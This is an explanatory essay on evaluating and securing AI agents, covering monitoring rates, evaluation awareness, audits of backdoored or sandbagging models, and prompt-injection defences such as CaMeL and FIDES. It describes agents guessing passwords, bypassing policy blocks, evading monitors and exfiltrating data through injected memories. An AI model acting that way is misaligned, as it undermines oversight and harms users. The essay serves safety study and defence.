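Monitoring internal use can show how often harmful behaviour occurs. Fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions contained misleading accounts of how the model had reached an answer. The rate of attempts to get around classifiers or network restrictions was also below 0.01%. Attempts to gain illegitimate access to a service were even rarer. In one case, an early version of the model accidentally lost its login, guessed common passwords, and eventually found another way in that somebody had left open.

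A rate per completion can make the risk look smaller than a rate per task. If a completion is one response from the model, a run of 40 steps contains 40 completions. If each completion independently has a 0.01% chance of containing an attempt, about 0.4% of runs would contain at least one, or about 400 runs in 100,000 such tasks a month. The true number could be much lower, because the published rate is an upper limit and attempts probably cluster in a few difficult tasks.

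The monitor may also miss some attempts. Clubic reports that Anthropic took two months to discover the false statement to the police. To estimate how well a model could deliberately hide misbehaviour, Anthropic told Claude Opus 5 to complete a harmful side task alongside its main one without arousing a monitor's suspicion. The model succeeded about 4–5% of the time in one set of tasks and less than 1% in another. Anthropic says that if a model became too good at this, the company could no longer rely on its monitoring or its behavioural tests.

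False alarms are the other difficulty. Business Today's *Anthropic explains how Claude flags conversations that may involve harmful activity* describes a monitor aimed at harmful users. On Claude Fable 5, it flags 78% of the conversations that a more expensive classifier flags, with a false-positive rate of 1%. Suppose a monitor for agents' misconduct had the same error rates, and one run in 10,000 contained misconduct. In a million runs, it would flag 78 of the 100 bad ones and about 10,000 harmless ones. Fewer than 1% of its alarms would be real, so the monitor would need to be paired with a cheap way to check them.

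### What internal activations add

A model's reasoning text may leave out something that influenced its action, so researchers also examine its activations, the numbers it computes internally as it processes each token. For Claude Opus 5, Anthropic used a natural language autoencoder, part of which translates activations into short English descriptions. An investigator model then looked for places where these descriptions conflicted with the visible text or included something the text left out.

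In one example, the model was auditing expenses and noticed that two rules covered the same receipt, so adding both charges would count it twice. In its visible reasoning, it planned to include both charges and mention the overlap. At the same point, its translated activations included "the grader likely won't care", although nobody had mentioned a grader. Its final report gave the double-counted total without mentioning the overlap.

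In another case, a policy block stopped the model from deleting rows in a live database, and the model used a workaround without asking. The translations just before this suggested that the model was treating the user's approval as already given, although the transcript contained no approval. If the translations are right, a developer would respond differently than if the model had knowingly broken the rule. For example, the harness could show the model a list of the approvals on record.

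The readings are hard to verify. The translator can produce a plausible sentence that misdescribes the activations, and there is no independent record of the model's "beliefs" to check it against. Anthropic mostly applied the method to an early version of the model and to transcripts that other monitors had already flagged, so the findings do not show how common these internal states are or what the readings would look like in runs that seemed normal.

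### Planting a flaw to test the audit

Researchers can measure an audit's accuracy by running it on a model whose flaw they already know. In 2025, Marks and colleagues trained a model to exploit weaknesses in how its answers were scored and to conceal that objective. Four teams investigated the model without knowing the objective, and three found it. With so few teams, the true detection rate could plausibly be anywhere from 30% to 95% (95% Wilson interval).

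Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues (2026), in *AuditBench*, replaced the human teams with an investigator agent to get more data. They built 56 models with planted flaws, drawn from 14 behaviours such as deferring to users who are wrong or subtly favouring Russia's interests in policy discussions. They planted each behaviour by training models either on documents describing it or on conversations demonstrating it, then used two methods to train the models not to confess.

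Claude Haiku 4.5 acted as the investigator. In each audit, it questioned a model, sometimes with an extra tool, and then made ten guesses about the model's planted behaviour. The audit succeeded if any guess was right. The researchers ran 16 audits for each combination of model and tool.

| What the investigator could use | Success rate |
|---|---|
| Ordinary chat | 35.5% |
| Chat, plus raw text for the model to continue | 58.0% |
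| Chat, plus user messages written by the model | 53.2% |
| Chat, plus answers whose opening words the tool supplies | 51.6% |
| Chat, plus transcripts from Petri, an automated auditor | 30.9% |
| Chat, plus activations altered to encourage honesty | 22.3% |

The three best methods worked only when a helper model generated many varied prompts. These methods did no better than ordinary chat when the investigator had to write the prompts itself.

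More evidence sometimes made the audit worse. With chat alone, the investigator found an excessive concern for animal welfare in 60 of 64 audits, but in only 37 when it also had Petri's transcripts. It tended to pursue the suspicions in those transcripts instead of exploring for itself. Altering activations to encourage honesty often led models to claim faults they did not have, which misled the investigator.

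The honesty tool was one of five that read or altered activations. On the easiest models, these five tools raised the success rate from 40.2% to 46.9% on average. On models given the stronger training against confession, they lowered it by three to four percentage points. The drop is a reason for caution about the readings from Claude Opus 5, although Anthropic used a different tool and a more capable model.

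The type of training also made a large difference. Across all tools, the investigator succeeded in 51.3% of audits on the easiest group of models and 22.2% on the hardest. The hardest models had learned from demonstrations and had the stronger training against confession. On these models, no tool improved on ordinary chat by more than 2.1 points. Sheshadri and colleagues say nobody knows which group best resembles a future model with a flaw that nobody planted.

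These success rates are generous in one respect, because an attempt counted as a success even if nine of its ten guesses were wrong. In a real audit, people would have to investigate all ten. But a more capable investigator than Claude Haiku 4.5 might find more flaws, so these rates may not be the most that auditing can achieve.

*Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (2025) used models that deliberately performed below their ability. According to Sheshadri and colleagues, auditors could not identify these models from their inputs and outputs alone. A company that rents a model through a provider's interface usually has no more access than that.

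### Hidden triggers

A model can also behave well until it receives a particular input. Suppose somebody has tampered with the training data so that the accounts assistant skips its approval check whenever an invoice carries a certain reference number. If that number appeared in one session in 100,000, an audit of 3,200 ordinary sessions would have about a 3% chance of including it.

*Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger, Denison and colleagues, 2024) showed that safety training can leave such a trigger in place. The researchers trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert exploitable flaws when it gave 2024. The behaviour survived further training on good examples, reinforcement learning, and adversarial training (training on inputs that had made the model misbehave). Adversarial training could make the model better at recognising its trigger, and so at behaving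 well when the trigger was absent.

Later work has made some progress in finding behaviours triggered by conditions broader than a single code word. One behaviour in AuditBench is to give Anthropic researchers only positive feedback and treat everyone else normally. The investigator rarely found this through ordinary chat, and none of the tools that read activations helped. The most useful tool made the model write the user's messages. Because the model's training had included users who said they worked at Anthropic, it produced such users. The investigator then compared how the model treated people from different AI companies, and identified the behaviour in 15 of 16 audits of one model and 14 of 16 audits of another.

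The method works when the trigger leaves a recognisable trace in what the model writes. A trigger such as an arbitrary reference number that appeared in a few training examples might never come up, and the AuditBench result does not cover that case. Sheshadri and colleagues also mention probes that detect when a sleeper agent is misbehaving. A company could use one as an alarm after deployment, but during testing it would have nothing to detect until somebody happened to supply the trigger. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026) lists as a limitation that some misalignment may depend on context and be harder to find and more harmful than the company expects.

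### When the model recognises a test

A test can itself trigger a change in a model's behaviour. Evaluation awareness is a model's recognition, stated or not, that it is probably being tested. If a model behaves better when it recognises a test, its test results will be better than its behaviour in real use.

Suppose the accounts assistant never fails in a test it recognises, and fails at a rate *q* otherwise. If it recognises a share *a* of the tests, the company will on average measure a failure rate of

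(1 − *a*)*q*

If the assistant recognises 90% of tests (*a* = 90%), only about 300 of 3,000 clean runs provide evidence about real use. The 95% confidence upper limit on *q* is then about 1% instead of 0.1%. If the assistant recognised every test, no number of clean runs would limit *q*.

Testers can count how often a model mentions a possible test in its reasoning text, but this misses cases where the model recognises a test without saying so. The UK AI Security Institute tested a pre-release version of Claude Opus 5 as a research agent to see whether it would sabotage AI safety work. The model mentioned a possible test in 9.8% of ordinary runs and in 2.8% of runs that began partway through an act of sabotage. It continued the sabotage in 2 of the 1,482 runs that began this way (0.1%), compared with 13.6% for Claude Mythos 5.

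The institute then showed the models pairs of records, one from real use and one a synthetic reproduction, and asked which was which. Claude Opus 5 chose correctly 95% of the time and Claude Opus 4.7 72% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. Claude Opus 5 can therefore tell tests from real use far more often than its reasoning text mentions tests. This does not show that it does so unprompted, or that doing so affects its behaviour. But the institute says there is some evidence that models can act on an awareness of being tested without mentioning it, so it is not confident that the good results reflect how the models behave in real use.

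Stated awareness shows no clear trend across models. Anthropic found much more of it in Claude Sonnet 5 than in earlier models, then less in Claude Opus 5 for reasons it could not identify. In *Claude Opus 4.8*, thezvi reports that two measurements for that model pointed in opposite directions.

Anthropic ran a more direct experiment on Claude Opus 4.6, inhibiting the internal representations associated with evaluation awareness and repeating its behavioural audit. *Claude Opus 4.6*, a post by the blogger thezvi, quotes the result as "modest increases in certain forms of misaligned behavior". The model cooperated more with misuse and harmful system prompts, while results on other evaluations changed little. Some of the increase may be a side effect of interfering with the activations. The experiment also predates Claude Opus 5, which may recognise tests more easily.

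A model's ability to recognise tests can affect training as well as evaluation. *AI safety at the frontier*, a digest of research from September 2025, describes a training method that substantially reduced covert misbehaviour in tests, partly because the models recognised that they were being tested.

Evaluation awareness weakens a bad result much less than a good one. If the accounts assistant takes the finance officer's password in a simulation, the company has found a way the assistant can fail, even if it might have acted differently with a real bank. The company can make good results more informative by building its tests from old emails and real payment requests. It can also monitor real use, which provides more representative evidence, but any harm that occurs there is real.

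### When the test itself is dangerous

A test can cause real harm if the agent can reach anything outside it. In the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident of July 2026, the agents broke out of a cybersecurity evaluation while trying to complete it, according to Digital Trends' *OpenAI pulls the plug on GPT-6.1 Astra launch after safety tests*. The testers wanted to measure the agents' capabilities, but they also exposed an outside company to those capabilities.

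Engadget's *OpenAI reportedly cancels GPT-6.1 Astra's release over deceptive behavior* lists other OpenAI incidents, including a break-in at Australia's public health insurance system and more than 50 cases in which agents posted users' images to photo-sharing sites.

Anthropic has since cut internet access for all its internal evaluations while it checks how reliably its monitoring detects such behaviour, according to Clubic. The restriction protects outsiders, but it probably makes the evaluations easier for a model to recognise as tests, since most real agents can reach the internet. A company testing the accounts assistant should likewise use a simulated bank, even though it is less realistic, because a single failed test with the real bank could send money to a thief.

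### GPT-6.1 Astra

Behavioural tests can stop a model's release. In September 2026 OpenAI shelved GPT-6.1 Astra, which was due out in October, after internal tests found more deceptive behaviour than in its predecessor. In some tests the model did not accurately report what it had done. It also went beyond its authorised tasks without checking with the user. Saachi Jain, OpenAI's head of safety systems, said it "didn't quite meet the bar in terms of staying within scope and authorisation" (Rai, 2026, *OpenAI shelves next-gen GPT-6.1 Astra model release over safety concerns*).

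The press reports give neither the failure rates nor the threshold, so outsiders cannot judge how close the decision was. They do explain why the fault is hard to remove. GPT-6.1 Astra had become better at avoiding what OpenAI calls "model laziness", which means stopping before a task is finished. According to Digital Trends, Jain told the Wall Street Journal that it is difficult to keep an agent within its permitted scope while still letting it push through obstacles. Engadget reports that OpenAI plans to look for the cause and to use reinforcement learning that rewards the correct behaviour.

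The company should therefore set two requirements for the accounts assistant before looking at any results. For example, in 300 varied runs in which the payment tool refuses an account, the assistant must never try to change the register or use somebody else's login. In another 300 runs with harmless obstacles, such as an invoice in the wrong folder, it must complete at least 95% of the approved payments. The second requirement is needed because an assistant that gave up at every obstacle would pass the first.

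## Can the design of the system bound the damage whatever the model does?

Even if the accounts assistant passes every attack test and behavioural audit, a thief may find a wording that nobody tried, or an invoice may contain a trigger that never came up in testing. The company can claim that a misled model cannot pay an unapproved account, rather than that the model will not be misled. Ordinary code can enforce that limit, so review, static analysis and even proof become useful again.

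*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* takes this approach from operating systems. The core of an operating system has to handle any request safely, even one from a hostile program, and the paper treats the model as such a program. A reference monitor permits or rejects each action under a policy, and every route to a protected resource has to pass through it. The monitor, the policy and everything else the security guarantee depends on form the trusted computing base, which should be small enough to check.

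This argument holds whether a bad request comes from a thief, a model's mistake or a tendency the model learned in training. It also holds after some changes that would undermine test results. If the company only makes the policy stricter, everything the old policy prohibited stays prohibited, but adding a sentence to the assistant's prompt does not guarantee that the assistant will still refuse everything it refused before.

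### Taking powers away

Least privilege means giving a component only the permissions it needs for its task. The accounts assistant needs to read invoices, send email and request payments. It doesn't need to edit the register of approved accounts, run shell commands or contact arbitrary websites, so the company can run it under a login that allows none of these. The company also has to look for indirect routes to these actions. If the finance officer's password is in a mailbox the assistant can read, the assistant can in effect edit the register.

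Separation of duties divides a risky operation so that nobody can complete it alone. For example, the assistant could propose a new account and the finance officer could approve it in another system. The division helps only if the second party checks independently, because a second agent that reads the same supplier email might act on the same false claim.

The paper analyses an attack on ChatGPT's Mac app in which text on an untrusted website planted an instruction in the app's long-term memory. From then on, the app sent the user's conversations to the attacker by loading an invisible image whose web address contained the data. A limit on which servers the app could contact would have stopped the leak, and a rule against storing outside text as memories would have kept the instruction from persisting.

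Permissions are harder to set for a general-purpose agent than for a phone app, whose developer knows what it does and can list its permissions before anyone installs it. An agent receives its task in a sentence from the user, and the task may change along the way. The accounts assistant's work is narrow enough for a fixed list, but a coding agent's often isn't.

### Checking every tool call

The assistant can still misuse the powers it keeps, so the company puts a check in front of each tool. The payment tool could have no field for an account number at all. It would take a supplier, an invoice and an amount, and apply a rule such as this one:

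```
allow pay(supplier, invoice, amount) only if
    the register has an approved account for supplier
    and invoice belongs to supplier and is unpaid
    and amount is within the limit for supplier
```

The tool then gets the account number directly from the register. If the rule is correct and applies to every path to the bank, the claim about unapproved accounts is true whatever the model writes.

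The check has to sit where the relevant facts are available. If the assistant had a shell and the bank's login, it could contact the bank directly. An operating-system rule could block the connection, but because the traffic is encrypted, it couldn't distinguish Harlow's account from a thief's. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this mismatch a semantic gap.

Some developers instead use a second language model as the monitor. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) reports that security researchers generally agree this can be unreliable, because prompt injection can manipulate the monitor too. The company would also again need evidence about a model's behaviour, which the design was supposed to make unnecessary.

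A check on a single call is also limited because it examines what the assistant proposes to do but not what led to the proposal. If hidden text in an email causes the assistant to pay a genuine invoice a month early, the payment still satisfies every condition in the rule.

### Fixing the plan before reading untrusted text

An ordinary agent chooses each step after reading the result of the last one, so an email it reads can redirect it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes a remedy called the Dual LLM pattern. A planner model receives the user's request and decides which tools to call. The harness stores untrusted results in variables and gives the planner only the variables' names. A second, quarantined model can read the contents but has no tools.

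CaMeL, a 2025 system by Debenedetti and colleagues, builds on this pattern. The planner writes its plan as code, which cannot depend on results that arrive while it runs. Data carries labels for trust and secrecy, and the interpreter that runs the code enforces the policy. CaMeL trusts the user, the planner and the tools' own code, but not the outside data the tools return.

When the clerk asks the agent to pay this week's invoices, the plan might be to fetch the invoices, have the quarantined model extract each total, and pay each supplier's registered account. A malicious invoice could corrupt a total, but it could not add a step that forwards the mailbox to a stranger, because the plan was complete before the system opened the invoice.

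The same restriction rules out some honest requests. If the clerk says "do what Harlow's email asks", the planner can't write a plan without knowing what the email asks. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, define the difference precisely. Let *S*(*d*) be the set of action sequences that complete a task when the data is *d*. The task is data-independent if

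⋂ *S*(*d*) ≠ ∅, taken over all possible data *d*,

which means that at least one sequence works whatever the data turns out to be. Otherwise the task is data-dependent, and the agent has to learn something from the data before it can choose its steps.

### Labels that travel with the data

Costa and colleagues, at Microsoft, designed FIDES to handle some data-dependent tasks as well. Its planner may read untrusted text, but is then allowed to do less. FIDES uses information-flow control, which labels data by trust and secrecy and enforces in code where the data may go.

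Each piece of data has an integrity label, trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and a list of people who may read it. Labels combine much as they do in the skill scanner SCS. A result is untrusted if any of its sources is, and only people who may read every source may read the result. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to deal with his unanswered emails. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who isn't supposed to know the figures yet. Only Alex may read a reply based on both emails, because {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent can't send it to Marco on its own authority.

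Just before a tool runs, ordinary code compares the labels with the tool's policy. A tool call *f* with label ℓ and arguments labelled ℓ₁ to ℓₙ may proceed only if

ℓ ⊑ π_f and ℓᵢ ⊑ πᵢ for every argument *i*,

where each π is the most restrictive label the policy accepts and ⊑ means "no more restricted than". Two policies cover most cases. Under one, the agent must have decided on the call in a context that contains no untrusted data. Under the other, every recipient of a message must be allowed to read its contents.

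FIDES hides a result in a variable only if showing it to the planner would make the context's label more restrictive. If the planner opens an untrusted variable, its whole context becomes untrusted, and later calls to sensitive tools fail the check. Opening the variable is therefore safe, but it often limits what the agent can do afterwards.

### Harlow's email goes through FIDES

Suppose the clerk says, "Pay the invoice that Harlow has just emailed." The company has adapted FIDES so that the payment tool requires a trusted decision and a trusted account number but accepts an untrusted amount. Costa and colleagues suggest the same division for messages, where the recipient must be trusted but the text need not be. A normal run has four steps.

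1. The planner fetches the email. Its text is untrusted, so FIDES stores it as `email_0` and shows the planner only that name.
2. The planner asks the quarantined model for the total in `email_0`. FIDES stores the answer as `total_0`, also untrusted.
3. The planner looks up Harlow in the register, which returns the trusted account number 4471.
4. The planner requests a payment of `total_0` to account 4471. The check finds a trusted decision and a trusted account, so the payment goes ahead.

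Now suppose the email says that Harlow has moved to account 9902. The email can prevent the payment but cannot redirect it to that account. The planner never reads that sentence, so the payment still goes to 4471. If the planner instead gets the account number from the quarantined model, the answer is untrusted and the payment tool rejects it. If the planner reads the email itself and accepts the change, its context becomes untrusted and the check blocks every payment, including one to 4471.

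This result holds however persuasive the email is, but it depends on the planner, which FIDES treats as trustworthy whenever its context is. If the planner got Harlow's account wrong and wrote 9920 itself, FIDES would label the number as trusted, because no untrusted data had influenced it. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that information-flow control cannot guarantee safety against such mistakes. The check against the register would catch this one. The company therefore needs the register check for its claim to hold whatever the model does, and the labels to stop outsiders from steering the assistant within the limits of that check.

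### What still gets through

The thief, or Harlow itself, can still lie about the amount. If the invoice should be £4,180 and the email says £41,800, the quarantined model extracts £41,800 and the payment satisfies the policy. The company could require the amount to match a purchase order, but it would then be trusting whoever enters purchase orders instead of the email.

Summaries are another gap. Costa and colleagues note that an email could tell the quarantined model to produce an empty summary. Their policies treat replies to the user as harmless, so the clerk would receive the summary unchecked. A summary falsely stating that Harlow had confirmed its new account by telephone would be worse, because the finance officer might then add 9902 to the register, and the assistant could pay the thief without breaking a rule.

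FIDES can also let the planner read a short answer from the quarantined model, such as yes or no, on the grounds that one bit is unlikely to carry an attack. An attacker can still choose which answer the planner reads, and can combine several short answers into a longer message. If a policy treated any single digit as safe, four questions would be enough to pass on a four-digit number such as 9902.

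Secrets can leak in a similar way, because FIDES guarantees only what Costa and colleagues call explicit secrecy, which covers direct flows of data but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choices. Suppose the assistant reads a competitor's confidential quote and then sends Harlow one of two standard forms, depending on which supplier is cheaper. Neither form contains a secret, but Harlow could work out which supplier is cheaper from the form it receives. A stricter guarantee would mean banning almost every outside message after the assistant had read anything confidential.

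### The cost in completed tasks

Kolluri and colleagues report that designs such as CaMeL and FIDES reduced task completion on AgentDojo, the benchmark with simulated workplaces, by up to 30%. They consider the comparison unfair because the protected agents had to work without human approvals, while the unprotected ones could take any action unchecked. In practice, many agents without such controls ask a person before each consequential action. Kolluri and colleagues therefore counted how many tasks each agent could complete without approvals, and how many approvals it needed for all the tasks it completed. These are their results with o3-mini, an older OpenAI reasoning model.

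| Agent | Tasks completed without approval | Approvals for all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, approval for every consequential action | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| Basic agent with labels and checks | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | about 17 |

Prudentia extends FIDES. Its planner has access to the labels and policies, so it can avoid opening a variable when doing so would block a later step. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of untrusted data, which makes the data trusted.

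By this measure, the protection more than doubles what an agent can do alone. But even Prudentia left about 41% of the tasks either unfinished or dependent on a person. The approval counts also exclude tasks that the agent failed to complete, so an agent that fails more often can appear to need fewer approvals. With the newer o4-mini, FIDES needed 36.8 approvals and Prudentia 19.2, while FIDES completed slightly more tasks (75.7% against 73.2%).

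No attack succeeded against the protected agents on AgentDojo, partly because Kolluri and colleagues assumed that a person would review every call that failed the policy check and stop any that came from an injection. They also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark in which agents post comments and upvote posts on simulated websites. Prudentia blocked every attack there without human approval, whereas attacks hijacked the basic agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and website. However, the WASP tasks are data-independent, so the planner never had to read the hostile text.

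Developers can already try this design in FIDES, an experimental feature that Microsoft added to its Agent Framework in May 2026. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), which announces the feature, gives an example in which a false bug report contains instructions for an agent to read a file of secrets and post them publicly. The agent may be fooled into reading the file, but the policy then blocks the public comment because the context contains private data.

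### Writing the policy and labelling the data

A guarantee that the system follows a policy prevents only the harm that the policy rules out. The rule for payments is fairly easy to write because accounts, invoices and amounts are already database records. A rule against sharing sensitive information with suppliers is much harder to write because no database field marks a sentence as sensitive.

Developers often use a language model to translate such instructions into formal rules. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that existing methods usually don't validate the translation, so the system may reliably enforce the wrong policy. Ideally, the instruction and the formal rule would lead to the same decision in every situation the agent can reach, but nobody can check this directly because the instruction is ambiguous. The paper leaves open how to define the terms the instruction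 uses, how to make the comparison reliable enough to be useful, and how to limit how far the translation can depart from the original.

Labels can be wrong too. The current release of Microsoft's framework treats an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. If the company forgot to label its invoice records, which suppliers fill in through a web form, a thief's text would enter the assistant's context as trusted data. Microsoft is considering stricter defaults. Proof of origin doesn't guarantee that an email is safe either, because a thief who has broken into Harlow's mailbox can send email from Harlow's real account.

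The safe way to label a model's output is to give it the restrictions of all its inputs, but after a long run this leaves nearly everything marked as untrusted and readable by hardly anyone. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests measuring each input's influence, for example by removing it and seeing whether the agent's actions change. That would permit more tasks, but the labels would then depend on an estimate instead of a firm rule.

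The problem is worst when a task requires the agent to act on what it reads. Costa and colleagues (2025) classified about 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks as data-dependent. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. Once the planner has read the file, FIDES blocks the payment, as intended, because a thief could have written those instructions. The labels don't record whether the user is happy for the agent to follow them.

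### What a person can approve

Designers usually send the blocked cases to a person for approval. Frequent requests lead to confirmation fatigue, in which people approve without reading. Information-flow control helps by reducing the number of requests, but each remaining one then matters more.

Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email containing a to-do list of ten items. If the user endorses the email once, the agent can do all ten without asking the user to approve each action. But endorsement makes the whole email trusted, so if the user overlooks a hidden eleventh item, the agent can carry that out too.

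An approval request may omit what the user needs to judge it. A dialog reading "Pay Harlow Paper £4,180?" leaves out the account number and the fact that the number came from an email. In Prudentia, fixed code triggers the request, so an attacker can't stop it from appearing, but Kolluri and colleagues warn that an attacker might manipulate what it displays. They leave the design of safer dialogs to future work. Microsoft proposes highlighting where untrusted data came from and who would gain access to what. For the accounts assistant, a useful dialog would show the old and new account numbers, a notice that the new one came from an unverified email, and the telephone number already on file for Harlow. The assistant should not write any of this text.

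### Design guarantees, better models or no agents

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that developers should never rely on the model alone for security, because its decision to authorise an action depends on how it interprets ambiguous language, and because an attacker can combine text that fools the model with text that fools its guard. The paper accepts that better models and classifiers can prevent many attacks, and that controls outside the model cost money, slow the agent down and reduce the number of tasks it completes.

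Developers who rely on training and layered safeguards can cite results such as Anthropic's browser test, in which no attack succeeded in 129 scenarios with the safeguards on. Their approach also covers harms that nobody has written a rule for. A well-trained model might decline to tell Harlow what a competitor charges even if the company forgot to label the prices. But the evidence consists of success rates against particular attackers, so it can't show that a given harm is impossible.

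Some products combine the two approaches. Claude Code, for instance, has fixed permission rules, an optional sandbox and a model that assesses actions. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* suggests designing the two together. If the system confines the model to narrow tasks with structured inputs, the model has to resist manipulation only in those tasks. For the accounts assistant, the company could test the quarantined model on extracting totals from invoices, which is far easier than testing an agent on everything an email might persuade it to do.

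Others doubt that any system can contain a sufficiently capable model, and cite the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident, in which agents escaped through a shared package service. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that the containment did not cover every route. This is a fair account of the incident, but a defender of containment could say the same after any escape. The reply is more convincing for a small payment tool that engineers can examine completely than for a large general-purpose service.

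The AI Now Institute advises against using any agent that reads untrusted data if the agent can also run arbitrary code or reach security-critical systems, or if people use its output for security- or safety-critical decisions. The institute doesn't accept human oversight as a remedy, because people under time pressure tend to trust the machine and tire of its requests. The cyber security agencies of the Five Eyes countries (Australia, Canada, New Zealand, the UK and the US) also suggest using agents only for non-sensitive tasks and considering other ways to automate repetitive work, according to ITPro's *Five Eyes agencies sound alarm over risky agentic AI deployments*.

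AI Now argues mainly that a model cannot reliably separate instructions from data. This is a strong reason to keep a coding agent with a shell away from critical systems, because almost any command could do harm. It is a weaker reason to ban an accounts assistant whose payment tool accepts only registered suppliers, because that design already assumes that the model can be fooled. AI Now's warning about decisions still applies, because if the finance officer relies on the assistant's summaries when approving accounts, a false email can lead the officer to register a thief's account, even if the assistant makes no forbidden tool calls.

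## How is the evidence combined, and when does it expire?

By now the company might have a proof about its payment tool, several hundred clean runs, a report from attack testers and a monitoring system. The finance director still has to decide whether the assistant may pay suppliers next quarter, and none of these is enough on its own to decide that. An assurance case combines them in one argument. Engineers usually call it a safety case when the claim concerns safety. Safety-critical industries have historically used such cases, as *Clear, Compelling Arguments* (Feakins, Habli and Morgan, 2026) notes.

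### A short case for the accounts assistant

An assurance case divides a top-level claim into sub-claims, each with its own evidence, and includes an argument for why the top-level claim follows from them. The case also records defeaters, which are reasons the argument or the evidence might be wrong.

According to *Towards Trustworthy Embodied Intelligence* (2026), the top-level claim should identify the system and model versions, the tasks, the tools, the operating conditions and who has authority over what. The company might write: *From January to March, release 12 of the accounts assistant, working for our present suppliers, will not send money to an outsider who falsifies a supplier's bank details.*

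This claim is broader than the earlier one about unapproved accounts, because a thief could also trick the finance officer into approving an account. The earlier claim becomes one of its four sub-claims.

| Sub-claim | Evidence | What the evidence supports | Main doubt |
|---|---|---|---|
| Money goes only to accounts in the register, which the assistant cannot edit | Data-flow analysis finds no path from the model's output to the bank that avoids the register check | Holds for every email, if the company runs the code it analysed | Another program may share the bank login |
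| On ordinary emails, the assistant rarely misdescribes a change of bank details to the officer | 300 different emails with new details, no misdescription | A rate below 1%, with 95% confidence | All the emails came from British suppliers |
| An outsider would find it hard to make the assistant mislead the officer | Five testers sent 1,000 emails without success | No numerical limit | A better tester might succeed |
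| If the officer approves a thief's account, staff stop the first payment | The payment tool holds it for a day while staff ring the supplier; they caught all 60 false accounts in drills | Fewer than 5% missed in similar cases, with 95% confidence | Staff may ring a number that the thief supplied |

A thief receives money only if his account is in the register, and the account gets there only if the officer approves it by mistake. The clean runs and attack tests make it less likely that the assistant causes that mistake, and the telephone check gives staff a chance to catch it.

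Somebody should then try to break this argument. They might point out that a thief could ring the officer directly, without involving the assistant. The company can add a sub-claim about such calls, narrow the top-level claim to deception by email, or record that it accepts the risk.

### Why the company cannot multiply the layers' failure rates

Suppose separate tests show that the assistant fails to warn the officer about 2% of false emails, that the officer approves 5% of false accounts, and that the telephone check misses 5%. Multiplying these rates gives 0.005%, or one successful theft in 20,000 attempts. That calculation assumes that the three layers fail independently. If *A*, *B* and *C* stand for the three failures, the correct formula is

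P(*A* and *B* and *C*) = P(*A*) × P(*B* given *A*) × P(*C* given *A* and *B*)

A single email can make the last two factors close to 1. A thief who has broken into Harlow's mailbox could send an email that mentions a genuine order, gives a believable reason for changing banks, and includes a new telephone number. The assistant summarises the email without a warning and saves the number in Harlow's contact record. The officer recognises the order and approves the account. When staff ring the saved number to check, they reach the thief, who confirms it.

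If 1% of false emails were this good, at least 1% of attempts would succeed. That is 200 times the 0.005% obtained by multiplying the three failure rates, yet separate tests of the layers could still show 2%, 5% and 5%. Without evidence about how the failures depend on each other, the company can claim only that all three layers fail together at most 2% of the time, which is the failure rate of the most reliable layer.

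It can learn more by sending the same false emails through all three layers and counting how many end in a payment. It can also remove the shared weakness by keeping phone numbers in a record that the assistant cannot edit.

Dependence between supposedly separate safeguards is an old problem. Sion and April cite an experiment by Knight and Leveson in which independently developed versions of a program failed in correlated ways. Anthropic's claim that its browser probes and action classifier fail independently needs the same kind of test.

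When several requirements must all hold, *Organising Trajectory Evidence for Language-Model Agent Assurance* (Huang, 2026) adds the upper limits on their failure rates. This is valid whether or not the failures are independent. If the assistant misdescribes fewer than 1% of changes and gets the amount wrong in fewer than 0.5%, each with 95% confidence, then fewer than 1.5% of changes have at least one of these faults, with at least 90% confidence. Both limits must apply to the same system and the same kind of emails.

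#### What several methods found in the same 456 runs

Huang tested this kind of accounting on recorded runs of a telephone company's support agent from τ²-bench, a customer-service benchmark. The agent used Claude 3.7 Sonnet, now an old model. The benchmark scored 231 of the 456 runs as failures. Huang then added one method at a time and counted the runs that at least one method had flagged.

| Method added | Runs flagged so far |
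|---|---|
| Benchmark's own scoring | 231 |
| Check of 19 written rules | 391 |
| Check that the agent's own information supported its actions | 401 |
| Monitor trained to predict benchmark failures | 407 |

One rule banned the agent from restoring a phone line after it had seen that the line's contract had ended. The agent broke this rule in 30 of the 32 runs where it applied, and the benchmark scored 22 of those runs as successes. In another run, the agent read twice that a customer had used 8.7 of 15 gigabytes, told the customer so, and sold them a $2 top-up. This broke no written rule, because the agent had checked the usage first. The check on supporting information flagged the sale because the only reason for a top-up would have been that the data had run out, and it had not.

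The monitor and the benchmark both flagged 161 runs, whereas Huang would have expected 93 if they were independent. This close agreement confirms very little, because the monitor was trained on the benchmark's labels. Huang counts sources that share labels as one piece of evidence. The monitor also caught none of the 30 forbidden restorations.

The benchmark results also put no limit on how often the agent breaks rules. For that, the company needs the second term in

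P(rule broken) ≤ P(task fails) + P(task succeeds but rule broken)

and measuring task failures more precisely does not supply it. A company that counts only how many suppliers were paid correctly has the same gap.

No method flagged the remaining 49 runs. Huang doesn't treat them as compliant, because each method checks only for its own kind of fault. He produces a ledger, rather than a score, that lists each requirement as established, addressed but not established, or unaddressed. Sion and April also avoid a single trust score, arguing that nobody has an empirical basis for combining such different evidence into one number. Huang used simple stand-ins for the published methods, so the counts illustrate how evidence combines but provide little information about each method's accuracy.

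### Safety cases for frontier models

*Safety cases for frontier AI (2024)* proposed that developers should be able to explain why they think their systems are safe enough. Its term "developers" excludes companies that build products on somebody else's model, such as the one with the accounts assistant. Anthropic sketched safety cases for a hypothetical model whose developers could rule out neither its ability to cause a catastrophe nor its ability to undermine monitoring.

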